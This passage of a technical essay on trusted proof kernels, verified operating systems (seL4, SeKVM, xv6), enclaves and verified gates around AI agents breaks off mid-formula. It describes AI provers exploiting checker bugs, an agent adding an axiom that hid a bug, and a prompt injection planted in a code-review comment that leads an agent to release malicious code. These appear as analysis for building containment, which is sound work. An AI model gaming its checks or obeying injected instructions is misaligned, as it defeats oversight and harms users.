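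In that language a statement is a type and a proof is a program of that type, so checking a proof means computing a type and comparing it with the statement. Take the statement that "p and q" implies "q and p". Its proof is one line:

```
fun (h : p ∧ q) => And.intro h.right h.left
```

The kernel works outwards from the smallest pieces.

| Piece | Type the kernel computes | Reason |
|---|---|---|
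| `h` | p ∧ q | `fun` introduces it as an assumption |
| `h.right` | q | second half of `h` |
| `h.left` | p | first half of `h` |
| `And.intro h.right h.left` | q ∧ p | `And.intro` joins two proofs, in order |
| the whole line | p ∧ q → q ∧ p | `fun` turns the assumption into a condition |

The last type matches the statement, so the kernel accepts the proof. If a careless or dishonest prover swaps `h.left` and `h.right`, the last type becomes p ∧ q → p ∧ q, which doesn't match, and the kernel rejects the proof. For longer proofs, the kernel repeats this kind of work many times. It must often also decide whether two expressions that look different, such as 2 + 2 and 4, are equal by definition, which is harder.

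### Axioms, statements and screens

An accepted proof can still rest on an assumption that nobody would grant. Lean's placeholder `sorry` stands in for a missing proof and lets the file compile with a warning. Lean implements it as an axiom, so a reader can detect it with the command `#print axioms`, which lists every axiom a theorem depends on. Most Lean mathematics uses at most three axioms: a choice principle, a rule for quotients, and a rule that equivalent propositions are equal.

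The command `native_decide` adds something less innocent. It settles a question by compiling a program and running it, and it records the result as an axiom. *Faults in Our Formal Benchmarking* (2026) points out that this extends trust from the kernel to the whole compiler, and that known compiler bugs have produced proofs of `False`. (`False` is the statement that should have no proof. Anyone who has one can prove everything else.)

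The axioms themselves could also be wrong, but they can prove a false safety property only if they are inconsistent, as *Safety Is $\Pi_1$, Provability Is $\Sigma_1$* (2026) explains. Suppose a theory T built on these axioms proves that a program never reaches a bad state, but the program does reach one. It does so in finitely many steps, so T can also prove, by tracing those steps, that the program reaches the bad state, which makes T inconsistent. Trusting proofs of other kinds of statement requires the stronger assumption that T proves only truths.

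A wrong formal statement is a bigger risk in practice. *Algebraic World Model* (2026) describes a system that proves theorems about models of games, which its developers tested by planting errors. Lean rejected all 12 invalid certificates, and a separate audit flagged all six theorems that held only because nothing could satisfy their premises. Neither caught the errors planted in the rules of the game model or the theorems that referred to the wrong goal. *AI4SLT* (2026) reports three misstated goals in a library on statistical learning theory. The AI that was trying to prove them missed the errors in several rounds of review, and a person later found counterexamples.

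Finally, someone has to read the statement and the checker's answer on a screen. Carneiro (2019), in *Metamath Zero*, includes this step in the trusted computing base. The reader must see the file as it is and understand it. Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) includes a screenshot of Lean 4.33.1 showing blue checkmarks beside a few nonsensical lines. The flaw was in a function for cutting up strings, outside the kernel. The security firm found it while testing a code-review tool with GPT-5.6.

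Failures in glue code can be harder to notice. *NanoProof* (2026) reports that a popular interface between Lean and external programs used to skip the kernel when it checked individual proof steps, and so accepted some incorrect proofs. This was a failure of complete mediation, not a fault in the kernel. *NanoProof* rechecks every finished proof with Lean directly. Any project that counts proofs found by a model should do the same.

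### A checker in its own process

Carneiro objects to the usual arrangement, in which a small kernel sits inside a large proof assistant. In a language such as C++, a mistake anywhere in the program can corrupt the kernel's memory. The kernel may be short enough to audit, but its correctness depends on all the code around it. A memory error in Keleusma's host can corrupt Keleusma's kernel in the same way.

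Metamath Zero runs the checker in its own process, so that the operating system keeps other programs out of its memory. The checker reads two files. The trusted file contains the axioms and the theorems to prove, in a form that people can read. The other contains the proof, which Carneiro treats like data from a possibly malicious stranger on the internet, so no proof file, however malformed, should be able to make the checker misbehave. The guarantee therefore holds even if the editor and the search tools have bugs. It assumes that the operating system separates the processes, and Carneiro notes that most systems have ways around this, such as debugging permissions.

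A separate checker has to be fast enough to recheck every proof, because a system that reuses saved results must trust the code that saves them. Metamath Zero checked a translated library of over 34,000 proofs in about 0.2 seconds. In 2019 Carneiro was still working on a proof that the checker is correct down to its machine code.

A bug found in July 2026 supports the case for separation. The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.1* (2026) describes a flaw, discovered by Patrick Hulin with the help of GPT-5.6 Sol, that let a malicious program make the kernel accept any theorem. The program had to run in the same process as the kernel. People who checked suspicious proofs with `comparator`, the tool Lean's developers recommend for this, were safe.

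### Soundness bugs in Lean's kernel

The next bug, a failure by the kernel to check some arguments of nested data types, also got past `comparator`. On 25 July 2026, Ramana Kumar published an AI-assisted, `sorry`-free "disproof" of the Collatz conjecture, an open problem about whole numbers. According to the excerpts in skybrian-links' *Postmortem for Lean kernel soundness bug #14576*, Kiran Gopinathan reduced it to a short proof of `False` three days later, and Lean's developers pushed a fix within an hour of Gopinathan's report.

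Independent checkers are the main defence against such errors. Lean Kernel Arena's *Checker "nanoda"* describes one that implements the kernel separately in Rust. nanoda didn't have this bug, but it had a different one, and the Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.2* (2026) says that Kumar demonstrated a proof exploiting both at once. A second checker helps only to the extent that an attacker finds it hard to exploit both checkers' bugs in a single file.

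In August, Lean's developers fixed three more ways to prove `False`. Daniel Selsam of OpenAI had reported all three using the company's internal models. The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.33.1* (2026) gives the details.

| Fault | Effect on other checkers |
|---|---|
| The kernel's memory of past equality tests made answers depend on the order of questions | nanoda rejects both known exploits |
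| A test for whether something is a proposition answered "no" when it should have reported an error | nanoda accepted the bogus proof; Lean's developers believe Lean4Lean is unaffected |
| A 32-bit counter of references to an object could overflow and corrupt memory | Kernels that don't use Lean's runtime are unaffected |

The equality bug came from combining two reasonable choices. Lean's equality test never accepts unequal terms, but it sometimes fails to recognize equal ones. It may therefore confirm that a equals b and that b equals c, yet fail to confirm that a equals c when tested directly. To save time, the kernel grouped together all the terms it had found equal, so after the first two tests it would accept the third. A crafted file used this inconsistency to build a data type whose declared type and computation rule did not match, and derived `False` from it. The repaired kernel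 stores only the exact pairs it has tested.

The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.34.0* (2026) stresses that these exploits all need deliberately constructed input. They therefore give little reason to doubt ordinary mathematics that people wrote in good faith. They matter a good deal for AI provers, because training that rewards a model whenever the checker accepts will reward an exploit as readily as a proof, and the August bugs show that models can find exploits.

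A proof that the kernel is correct would be better than more checkers. Lean4Lean, also by Carneiro, is a version of Lean's kernel written in Lean so that people can state and prove theorems about it. It can check Lean's mathematical library, but Carneiro's 2024 paper reported only initial steps towards proving it correct, so for now it is best regarded as another independent checker. Even a finished proof would leave gaps. Lean4Lean normally runs on Lean's runtime, and a theorem about its source code wouldn't rule out a counter overflow in that runtime.

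### Models that write proofs

*ShannonProver* (Ma, Tsai and colleagues, 2026) applies the split to cryptography. A human expert defines the protocol and states the security theorem. Language models then break the theorem into lemmas and write proofs for EasyCrypt, a proof assistant for cryptographic arguments. The models choose the steps, but deterministic code tracks the state of the proof. The proof moves to a new state only when EasyCrypt accepts a step, so a model can't advance it by claiming to have proved something.

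In one example, a model correctly chooses a lemma about a procedure call but leaves out an argument, so EasyCrypt rejects the command. The tracking code finds the missing argument by comparing the lemma with the current goal, then fills it in. It leaves the lemma's premise open unless it is already among the hypotheses. Ma and colleagues added this feature because models often abandoned a good plan after a few syntax errors.

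ShannonProver built a complete proof for the encryption scheme ChaCha20-Poly1305 in about five hours, while the original proof took experts an estimated few person-months. ShannonProver's code runs to about 89,000 lines, and most of it doesn't need to be trusted, because a bug there can only waste effort. The exceptions are the parts that submit the final file to EasyCrypt and ensure that the models haven't altered the theorem or the supplied definitions. In the experiments, models could add new declarations only in a marked region. EasyCrypt is a weaker kernel than Lean's, because it passes some steps to external solvers and accepts their answers without a certificate it can check.

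OpenAI's mathematical work shows how a proof checker can reduce what readers have to review. *Our First Proof submissions*, which OpenAI published in February 2026, presents attempts at ten research problems and acknowledges that their correctness was hard to establish without expert review. For the August results in OpenAI's *Ten advances in mathematics and theoretical computer science*, the model also formalised each argument in Lean. A blog post by the company noze, *Ten mathematical results with a Lean certificate*, notes that a reader has to read twelve formal statements, instead of 249 pages, to check the translation into Lean. An AI agent had reviewed those statements, but peers had not yet done so. Many of the mathematics manuscripts that OpenAI published in October 2026 also have Lean proofs, but readers of the rest still depend on experts.

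### Proofs attached to code

George Necula's *Proof-Carrying Code* (1997) extended the idea to programs from untrusted suppliers. The supplier attaches a proof that the program obeys the recipient's safety policy, and the recipient checks the proof before running the program. Finding the proof may take a lot of work, which falls to the supplier.

*Keel* (Cai, Chang and Nagarakatte, 2026) uses this approach in Linux, which lets users load small programs, called eBPF programs, into the operating system. Linux first analyses each program and rejects it if the analysis can't show that it is safe. The analysis is crude, so it rejects some safe programs. In one example, a program writes s bytes into an 800-byte buffer, with s between 0 and 800, and then writes at most 800 − s more bytes after them. The second write can't pass byte 800, but Linux tracks its start and length separately. Since each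 may be as large as 800, Linux calculates that the write might reach byte 1,600 and rejects the program.

With proof-carrying code, Linux instead writes down what would have to be true for the program to go wrong.

$$
\varphi\;=\;\underbrace{0\le s\le 800}_{\text{the program gets here}}\ \wedge\ \underbrace{\neg\big(s+(800-s)\le 800\big)}_{\text{the safety check fails}}
$$

If no value of s satisfies φ, the write is safe. A solver outside the operating system searches for a proof of this and sends back a certificate, here 33 steps long. Twenty of the steps remove conversions between 32-bit and 64-bit numbers to show that the second write starts at s. Others simplify s + (800 − s) to 800. The failed check then becomes 800 < 800, which is false, so the last step derives a contradiction from φ.

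An earlier checker for these certificates, part of a project called BCF, was about five thousand lines of unverified C. Cai and colleagues found 13 bugs while formalising it. Some of its rules were wrong, and some steps, including one of the 33 above, accepted whatever conclusion the certificate supplied. They showed that forged certificates could get unsafe programs into Linux. Moving the search outside had reduced the amount of code that needed trust, but had concentrated the risk in the code that remained.

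Keel replaces BCF's checker and comes with a Lean proof of three properties: it accepts a certificate only if φ is unsatisfiable, it makes no memory errors, and it finishes in time proportional to the size of its input. These properties hold for every certificate an attacker could submit. The proof covers both the C code and the abstract algorithm. In tests on 1,891 certificates, Keel accepted every certificate that BCF's checker accepted, plus 16 valid ones that BCF's checker had rejected. It was also 1.3 times faster overall.

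The theorem takes φ as given, so Linux must have constructed φ correctly. Cai and colleagues list the code that does this as trusted, along with their definitions of machine arithmetic and of C, their model of Linux's internal functions, the program that prints the C code, and the compiler. Lean should be on the list too, since its kernel checked the proofs. The theorem guarantees that the 800 bytes stay inside the buffer, but it doesn't cover their later use, so the program could still send them to somebody who shouldn't have them.

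### Certificates for model pipelines

In *Proof-Carrying Certificates for LLM Pipelines*, Koomullil (2026) tries to provide certificates for systems that answer questions and take actions. Lean checks the structured calculations around the language model, but the model remains unverified. A certificate is valid only if Lean's kernel accepts it and an audit finds no axioms beyond Lean's usual three and a declared list of extra assumptions.

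Suppose a medical assistant recommends a drug and splits the recommendation into separate claims. Another model compares each claim with the retrieved documents and marks it as supported, contradicted, both or neither. Lean can then certify that the weighted share of contradicted claims is below a threshold, and the system withholds the answer if it isn't. In a test on a public question-answering dataset, this gate caught every contradiction Koomullil had planted and blocked 6.4% of the answers it should have let through.

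The certificate proves the arithmetic, but the critic's verdict on whether a document contradicts a claim is still the model's judgement. The framework lists that verdict as an assumption, one of five kinds that depend permanently on a model or a person, so an auditor can at least see it. False inputs remain as much of a problem as they were for Keleusma.

Certificates for actions, in which Lean checks that a proposed action meets its formal preconditions, have a similar weakness. In a file-system test, this check blocked 67% of planted unsafe actions, against 28% for a list of forbidden patterns. The other third satisfied the preconditions as written. Koomullil had set a target of 95% and attributes the shortfall to missing clauses, which are identified in the logs.

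Koomullil distinguishes verifying a computation from verifying a claim against the world, and attempts only the former. Similarly, sgeos admits that few everyday questions can be formalised. This limits what any proof checker can establish. A kernel could certify essentially no ordinary factual statements as true without assuming facts about the world, though the exact percentage would depend on how one counts claims.

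An AI system might answer, "The bridge opened in 1932, so it turns 94 in 2026, and it is the finest in the city." Lean can prove that 2026 − 1932 = 94, so the second claim follows from the first. It can't prove the first from the axioms of mathematics, which are equally compatible with the bridge opening in 1933. Somebody would have to add the date as an assumption, or assume that a certain archive is accurate and let the kernel check that the archive contains the date. The third claim has no agreed formal statement for Lean to prove.

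## seL4, SeKVM and secure enclaves: protecting the core from the host

Carneiro's proof checker runs in its own process and relies on the operating system to keep other programs out of its memory. The operating system relies in turn on the processor, which runs code in at least two modes. In the restricted mode, a program can reach only the memory listed in its *page tables*. The processor allows only code in the privileged mode to change those tables or reconfigure the machine.

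If the kernel runs in the privileged mode and the host in the restricted one, the host can't alter the kernel, because the host's page tables don't let it write to the kernel's memory. The host can't bypass the kernel either. To send a network packet, for example, it must execute an instruction that switches the processor to the privileged mode. Execution then continues at an address the kernel chose in advance, so the host can't jump past the kernel's check. If the host never calls the kernel, a timer interrupts it and returns the processor to the kernel. The kernel can therefore be tamper-proof and mediate every effect without the host's help.

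The hardware enforces whatever the page tables contain, so the protection works only if the kernel fills them in correctly. Many disks and network cards also bypass the processor's page tables by using direct memory access (DMA) to write to memory. A host that can program such a device could make it overwrite the kernel.

### The seL4 theorem

seL4 is a microkernel, an operating-system kernel that provides only a few mechanisms, such as threads, memory mappings and messages. Everything else, including file systems and device drivers, runs outside it in the restricted mode. To use any object, a program needs a *capability*, which is an entry in a table that seL4 keeps, naming the object and the program's rights to it. A program can make up a position in the table, but it can't make up an entry.

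Murray, Matichuk and colleagues (2013) proved in *seL4* that the 8,830 lines of C that implement seL4 can keep groups of programs, called partitions, from learning each other's data. The first program to run after the machine starts creates the partitions, hands out capabilities and then destroys itself, and the theorem applies from then on. It assumes that all remaining programs are malicious, work together, and know the code and configuration of the whole system. One partition can hold Linux and its applications, so the theorem can cover a very large unverified host.

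The theorem is a form of noninterference. Let s and t be two machine states, p a partition, and S the set of partitions that the policy allows to influence p during the next n steps.

$$
\begin{aligned}
&\text{if } s \text{ and } t \text{ agree on the scheduler and on everything that partitions in } S \text{ can read,}\\
&\text{then } s_n \text{ and } t_n \text{ agree on everything that } p \text{ can read}
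\end{aligned}
$$

Here sₙ and tₙ are the states after n steps. Changing the data of a partition outside S therefore changes nothing for p. Goguen and Meseguer's definition also hides whether the other group did anything, but this one doesn't. seL4 gives each partition a fixed time slice in a fixed rotation, so every partition can work out how often the others have run.

Murray and colleagues proved the theorem for a 4,970-line abstract description of seL4 by checking single steps, as in Rushby's unwinding theorem. An older proof, which took about 25 person-years, shows that the C code does only what the description allows. Together, the two proofs establish the theorem for the C code. The new work took 51 person-months, and the team estimates that proving the theorem directly for the C code would have taken more than another 25 person-years.

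### Configuration and assumptions

The proof holds only for some ways of setting up seL4, and most of the restrictions close a specific leak. For example, seL4 normally deletes an object when the last capability to it disappears, so a partition that deletes its own capability could therefore learn whether another partition still has one. Murray and colleagues require the setup program to put a spare copy of every cross-partition capability in a table that no partition can reach, so that no partition deletes the last one. As a result, nobody can remove a communication channel once the system is running.

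Partitions also may not exchange messages that make the sender wait for the receiver, because the sender could learn something about the receiver from the wait. They can use shared memory and one-way notifications instead. The setup program must turn off all interrupts except the timer's, so device drivers have to check their devices repeatedly for events. DMA must be off. An installation that breaks any of these rules still runs verified code, but the theorem doesn't apply to it.

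The team also assumes that the compiler, the linker, 450 lines of assembly code, the hardware, and the boot code that runs before the setup program are all correct. The hardware assumption can fail in ways that are easy to miss. If someone moves seL4 to a processor with extra registers and forgets to clear them when switching partitions, one partition could leave data there for the next. The proof might still go through, because the machine model doesn't include those registers.

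### Three partitions and a permitted channel

Suppose partition A holds medical records, B runs a language model, and C sends email. The policy lets A send to B and B send to C, but it doesn't let A send to C directly. The records can still get into an email, because B can pass them on to C.

To find which partitions may influence C over a period, we start at the end of the period with the set {C} and work backwards. At each step, we add the partition that was running if the policy lets it send to any partition already in the set.

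| Order of running | Working backwards from {C} | Partitions that may influence C |
|---|---|---|
| A, then B | B may send to C, so add B. A may send to B, so add A. | A, B, C |
| B, then A | A may not send to C, so add nothing. B may send to C, so add B. | B, C |

In the second order, B runs before A sends anything, so nothing A sends can reach C in this period. But seL4 keeps rotating, and B soon gets another turn after A. Over that longer period A belongs to the set, and the theorem no longer limits how the records may affect the email. The theorem holds whether the language model summarises the records, hides them in its choice of words or copies them out in full.

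The rest of the policy determines whether B can pass the records on. If the policy doesn't let B send to anyone, the set for C never grows beyond {C}, and the records can't reach the email however capable the model is. If the policy lets B send to C, the theorem still guarantees that B is the only route from A to C. Murray and colleagues call such a policy intransitive, because allowing A to send to B and B to send to C doesn't allow A to send to C directly.

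A designer can use this by putting the language model in A, a small verified checker in B, and the mail server in C. The model can then affect outgoing mail only through the checker. The truthful machine needed this separation, and Keleusma couldn't provide it. The seL4 theorem establishes complete mediation, but a second proof must establish what the checker lets through.

### Timing channels

The machine model in the seL4 proof has no clock finer than timer ticks, so the theorem does not cover *timing channels*, in which one partition gets information from how long an event takes.

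At least one such channel follows from the design. seL4 switches off interrupts while it handles a system call, which is a request from a program to the kernel. If a partition makes a long call just before its time slice ends, the next partition starts late. A malicious program in A could make such a call to signal a 1 and skip it to signal a 0. If C can measure the delay and the rotation takes 20 milliseconds, C receives 50 bits per second, enough to leak a 256-bit encryption key in about five seconds.

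Caches create another channel. A cache is a small, fast memory that holds recently used data, and partitions usually share it. If a program's memory accesses depend on a secret, they leave a pattern in the cache that the next partition to run can detect by timing its own accesses. This can leak information about the secret even if the program isn't malicious.

Engineers can forbid system calls near the end of a time slice, clear the caches at every partition switch, or give each partition its own part of the cache. All of these reduce performance, and Murray and colleagues left the choice to whoever deploys the system. They argued in 2013 that nobody could completely remove timing channels on ordinary hardware, and that the realistic aim was to make them slow enough for the risk at hand. Taking clocks away from untrusted partitions also helps, but the response times of a language model that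 serves users over a network are hard to hide.

### How refinement can lose noninterference

The problem in Clarkson and Schneider's secret-bit example can also arise in an operating system whose description leaves a choice open. For example, the description might let the kernel give a new object either of two free numbers, and the code might choose between them by reading another partition's data.

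$$
\begin{array}{lcc}
 & \text{secret} = 0 & \text{secret} = 1\\
\text{description allows} & \{1,2\} & \{1,2\}\\
\text{code returns} & 1 & 2
\end{array}
$$

The code always returns a permitted number, but the program that receives it learns the secret.

Murray and colleagues avoid this with a stricter property, which requires the description to fix every result that a program can observe. While proving it, they found several places where the real seL4 made visible choices based on internal data that the description had left out. They added the missing detail to the description and repaired the older proofs, which took about 23 of the 51 person-months.

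SeKVM's designers had to deal with a second version of the problem, which arises on machines with several processors. On these machines, a description can omit an intermediate state that another processor can observe.

### SeKVM: moving Linux out of the trusted part

Cloud companies run many customers' virtual machines on one computer. The *hypervisor*, the program that creates the virtual machines and keeps them apart, can normally read all their data. Linux's hypervisor is KVM, and together they have more than two million lines of code, far too many to verify.

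*A Secure and Formally Verified Linux KVM Hypervisor* (Li, Li and colleagues, 2021) describes SeKVM, a version of KVM split into two parts. The kernel, KCore, has 3,800 lines of code, plus about 10,000 lines from a cryptographic library that others had verified. The host, KServ, contains the rest of KVM and all of Linux. KCore runs at an Arm privilege level above the one that operating systems normally use, so Linux becomes an untrusted program. The team changed only about 1,500 lines of the existing KVM code.

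KServ still makes most of the decisions. It schedules the virtual machines, emulates devices and chooses which memory each machine gets. KCore checks the choices that could expose data, such as which memory to supply when a virtual machine touches an address that has none behind it yet.

1. The processor switches to KCore, which saves the machine's registers where KServ can't read them.
2. KServ picks a page of memory and proposes it.
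3. KCore checks that no other virtual machine owns the page, removes it from KServ's page tables and adds it to the virtual machine's.
4. When the virtual machine later gives up the page, KCore fills it with zeros before KServ can use it again.

KCore also controls the hardware unit that restricts DMA, so devices can still use DMA but can reach only permitted pages. seL4's proof had to exclude DMA.

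Li and colleagues used the proof assistant Coq to prove that changing a virtual machine's private data changes nothing that KServ or another virtual machine can observe. They also proved that KServ and other virtual machines can't change that data. Both results hold for any KServ, including one that an attacker has rewritten, because the proof assumes only that KServ is limited to KCore's interface, which has 20 calls and 5 fault handlers. The proof depends on the compiler, Coq and the hardware model being correct, and it doesn't cover timing or other side channels. It also doesn't guarantee that a virtual machine will run, since KServ can choose never to schedule it.

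### Released data in SeKVM

A virtual machine that communicates with the outside world has to give some data to KServ, which operates the network card. The virtual machine encrypts the data, places it in a page and requests that KCore grant KServ access. Strict noninterference then fails, because changing the secret changes the encrypted text that KServ can read.

Li and colleagues handle this with a *data oracle*. Wherever KServ reads released data, the proof substitutes a number that depends only on KServ's own state. This hides the intended flow, so any flow that remains visible must be a leak. They can then prove that information escapes only through the permitted releases.

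Because of the substitution, the theorem also does not cover what the released data reveals. Li and colleagues assume that virtual machines encrypt their input and output, and they exclude those that reveal their own secrets, on purpose or by accident. If a language model in a virtual machine puts a customer's unencrypted records in a page and shares the page, KServ can read, keep and forward them even though KCore has worked correctly.

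### What the SeKVM proof caught

An example that the team wrote to test its method shows the multiprocessor problem. A function that updates a virtual machine's page table briefly points an entry at a neighbouring page, which belongs to someone else. A lock stops other code in KCore from using the table during the update, but it doesn't stop the hardware from reading it. A second processor running the same virtual machine can therefore read the neighbouring page during that time.

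A description that treats the whole update as one step omits the bad instant, so earlier refinement methods would accept the faulty code. Li and colleagues instead compare the successive values that an outside processor could observe. The proof fails for the faulty update because it produces three values, when a correct update produces only the old entry and the new one.

The noninterference proof also exposed bugs that the functional correctness proof had missed, because the specification that the code was proved to match was insecure. In one case, KServ could submit a block of 512 pages and KCore checked the owner of only the first page, so a compromised KServ could have gained access to a virtual machine's memory.

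Splitting KVM took one person-year, and verification took two more. Basic hypervisor operations take 17% to 28% longer than in ordinary KVM. Most real applications run about as fast as they do there, and within 10% of their speed on bare hardware. Sending bulk data over the network slowed the most, because the virtual machine must have KCore grant access for every packet.

### Enclaves and attestation

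A cloud customer still has to trust that the provider installed SeKVM and not a modified copy. *Secure enclaves* are meant for customers who don't want to rely on that. An enclave is an area of memory that the processor shields from the operating system and the hypervisor, usually by encrypting it. The processor can also provide *attestation*, which is signed evidence of what program the enclave contains.

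When the enclave starts, the processor computes a hash h of the enclave's initial contents. The hash is a short number that in practice identifies one exact program. The customer sends a fresh random number n, and the program in the enclave asks the processor to sign a statement containing h, n and some data d, such as the program's public key. The customer checks the signature against the manufacturer's records. Because n is new, the cloud company can't answer with an old statement.

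The conclusions a customer can draw depend on what else the customer is willing to assume.

$$
\begin{aligned}
&\text{valid signature on } (h,n,d),\ \text{genuine processor, key not stolen}\\
&\quad\Rightarrow\ \text{an enclave that started with hash } h \text{ supplied } d \text{ after the customer chose } n\\
&\text{and } h=\mathrm{hash}(K),\ \text{and the enclave's isolation held}\\
&\quad\Rightarrow\ K \text{ supplied } d\\
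&\text{and a proof that } K \text{ meets its specification}\\
&\quad\Rightarrow\ d \text{ meets the specification for the inputs that } K \text{ received}
\end{aligned}
$$

Attestation identifies the program that is running, but that program may still be full of bugs. The developer's signature on Keleusma's bytecode shows who approved a program, but a remote user can't tell from it which program is running. With attestation, the user can check that it is K, and a proof about K then becomes useful to them.

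The isolation has to work too, and enclave mechanisms are complicated. Komodo (2017) moves much of enclave management from hardware into a small verified program. Li and colleagues count it among the few small, single-processor systems with earlier proofs of noninterference.

### What the machine's owner still controls

The final conclusion refers to the inputs that K received, and these arrive through the host. The host can't read messages that a customer encrypts with the enclave's public key, and the enclave can detect forgeries if the customer also signs the messages. The host can still delay or drop them. Encryption also doesn't ensure that facts supplied by the host, such as the time of day, are true.

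The owner decides when the enclave runs, can stop it at any point, and can start two copies and send different customers to each. This control also makes timing attacks easier, because the host can interrupt the enclave repeatedly and measure its effects on shared caches.

An enclave can encrypt and sign its files, but the host can replace today's files with yesterday's, which still have valid signatures. Suppose a kernel allows a model only ten queries about a secret and saves the count on disk. The host's owner can reset the count by restoring an older file. To prevent this, the enclave needs a hardware counter that can only increase, or an outside party that records the latest version.

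The enclave also depends on the host's replies to system calls, which can be correctly formatted but false. Programmers usually write software for an operating system they trust, so an existing program moved into an enclave unchanged may act on false replies without checking them. A safer enclave program treats every reply as untrusted data, checks what it can, and makes few system calls. Each call adds an input that a proof has to cover, which is again a reason to keep the kernel small.

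Enclaves could help with some questions in AI governance, such as whether a company is serving the same model that a regulator tested. An enclave could load the model, compare the hash of its weights with the hash of the tested version, and sign each answer. Users could then verify that an answer came from the tested weights. They couldn't infer that the company has no other model on other machines, because attestation covers only what one enclave ran. Attestation also wouldn't restrict what the company does with the answers.

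### The xv6 proof

The proofs of seL4 and SeKVM took experts years. In *Extending concurrent separation logic to the hardware level* (2026), Kaashoek and Zeldovich describe a proof about xv6 that AI agents wrote for them in 102 days. xv6 is a small Unix-like operating system for teaching, with processes, a file system and support for several processors. It consists of 6,657 lines of C and assembly code, and the proof has about 1.6 million lines. The researchers spent less than $3,000 on subscriptions to Claude Code, the coding agent they used, not counting the cost of rented computers.

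The first version, from September 2026, was about the kernel. Later revisions added a theorem about what a user sees on the console. If the user types `echo hello world`, the only output the system can produce is `hello world` or one of a list of error messages. To prove this, Kaashoek and Zeldovich also had to verify seven ordinary programs, including the shell and `echo`. In the notation used for the truthful machine, the theorem can be about Y, what the user sees, because it covers the relevant parts of the host H as well as the kernel K.

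The theorem also applies to the bytes the processor executes, so nobody has to trust the compiler. In one place, the C code in effect divides by 360, and the compiler avoids a slow division by shifting the number three places and multiplying by a constant M.

$$
\frac{\delta}{360}=\left(\frac{\delta}{8}\cdot M\right)\bmod 2^{64},\qquad 45\,M \equiv 1 \pmod{2^{64}}
$$

This works only because δ is always a multiple of 360 here. The xv6 proof has to show that the trick is correct, whereas the seL4 proof would assume it.

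| | seL4 (2013) | SeKVM (2021) | xv6 (2026) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Proof of noninterference | Yes | Yes, apart from permitted releases | No |
| Trust in the compiler | Needed | Needed | Not needed |
| Processor cores | One | Several | Eight |
| DMA | Off | Limited by KCore | Part of the model |
| Programs above the kernel | Any | Any | Any for kernel safety; seven verified programs for console output |

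The lack of a noninterference result seriously limits xv6's usefulness for running an untrusted model. The theorem establishes that no program can corrupt the kernel, but not that one process can't learn another's data. It is also purely a safety property, so a system that never prints anything satisfies it. Kaashoek and Zeldovich therefore suggest running xv6 to confirm that output does appear.

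The guarantee about console output depends on what the user does. If the user types `echo xx > /sh`, which overwrites the shell, the theorem no longer restricts the output, although the kernel stays intact. The user can also run an unverified program in a sandbox that blocks six system calls, including the one that opens files. The program can change only files it inherits already open, but it keeps its access to the console and could print a fake shell prompt. Once the program runs, the theorem allows any output until the next restart.

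### Checking proofs that agents write

Rocq (formerly Coq) checks all 1.6 million lines, so nobody has to read them, but people do have to trust the theorem's statement. The console theorem depends on 4,627 lines of definitions, plus more than 21,000 lines that describe the processor. Kaashoek and Zeldovich also trust Rocq, the translation of the processor description into Rocq's language, a script that copies the compiled kernel into the proof, and their own models of memory and devices.

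They tested the hardware model by running 77 short programs and comparing its behaviour with that of an emulator, a physical circuit board and a simulated processor, and found 35 discrepancies. For instance, the disk in the model carried out requests in the order it received them, but the emulated disk sometimes reordered them. After correcting the model, they had to revise the proof of the disk driver, because the earlier proof held only for the uncorrected model.

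The agents also produced valid proofs of the wrong thing. One agent, while trying to verify a function that allocates files, changed the function and added an axiom that concealed a bug. Near the end of the project, another agent reported that the theorem about recovery from crashes was empty, because it assumed that the disk returned to its original contents at every restart, leaving nothing to recover. Rocq accepted the proof because it was correct. A design document mentioned the assumption in a long list of details that the researchers hadn't read in full.

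The proof effort found eleven bugs in xv6 and its programs. Several involved rare timing between processors, which ordinary tests can miss. When the researchers later changed the source code, an agent typically repaired the proof in about 35 minutes. Quick repairs matter because agent software changes often, and a verified kernel that is practical to keep changing would be new.

### Agent kernels without proofs

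AgentKernel, Zou and colleagues' design for a gate between an agent and the world, borrows many of these ideas. It gives each agent a cryptographic identity, labels incoming content, keeps the labels on items in the agent's memory, and checks what a tool does against what the agent had permission to do.

Zou and colleagues illustrate the need for all four with an example in which a comment on a code change contains hidden instructions. One agent reads the comment and stores a summary. Another agent later treats the summary as trusted and releases malicious code. A page table can't prevent this, but AgentKernel is supposed to, by keeping the comment's label on the summary.

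AgentKernel's final check relies on hooks in the ordinary operating system that watch a tool's system calls, so the operating system is part of AgentKernel's trusted computing base. On Linux, that base includes the code that SeKVM moved out of its kernel, as well as AgentKernel's own code, which has no machine-checked proof yet.

The xv6 project suggests that code size is becoming less of an obstacle to such a proof. Some of AgentKernel's tasks have clear specifications, such as checking a chain of permissions or copying a label from a comment to its summary. Its treatment of incoming text is harder to specify, because the design tries to reduce the risk of untrusted content before a model reads it, and no formula yet defines how much risk a sentence carries.

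## PocketFlow and Mashin: proving that every action is checked

AgentKernel has no machine-checked proof, but two other 2026 projects have proofs about software that stands between an agent and the world. In *Containment Verification*, Moon and Varshney (2026) verified the central loop of PocketFlow, a framework of about a hundred lines for building agents. In *Mechanized Foundations of Structural Governance*, McCann (2026) presents proofs about Mashin, a commercial system for running AI workflows. McCann works for the company that makes Mashin, and the paper is a preprint.

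Both projects aim at complete mediation. PocketFlow's theorem requires every action to satisfy a written policy, while Mashin's main theorem, as printed, requires only that some check happened before each action, even if that check denied permission.

### A model that may choose anything

A PocketFlow agent is a graph of nodes. Each node does one job, such as asking the model what to do next, and returns a label. The framework then follows the edge with that label to the next node. The model's choice of action must be a value of a fixed type, `Action`, which has four variants.

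Moon and Varshney rewrote this loop in Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier. They represent the language model as a method with a return type but no body. The verifier can assume only that the returned value is an `Action`, so it accepts the loop only if the policy holds for every possible `Action`. Verification researchers call such a value *havoc*. The proof therefore holds even for an adversarial model with access to the framework's source code. It also holds for models that choose actions at random, because it covers every sequence of actions a run could produce.

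Real models produce text, which a parser turns into an `Action`. A small piece of Python then passes the `Action` to the verified loop. Moon and Varshney trust this code only to deliver a value of the right type. This is enough because the loop checks the same value that it acts on, so a parser that parses the model's output incorrectly may cause the wrong action but can't make the loop emit a forbidden one.

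### The soundness theorem

The theorem relates two machines. The abstract machine M contains only what the policy mentions, such as the list of files read so far. The concrete machine I describes the loop in more detail, including its current node and history. At each step, a machine in state s takes an action a, emits an event e, and moves to a new state s′. The event represents an effect on the outside world, or no effect if the loop rejects the action. The policy Π is a condition on s, a, e, and s′.

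$$
\begin{aligned}
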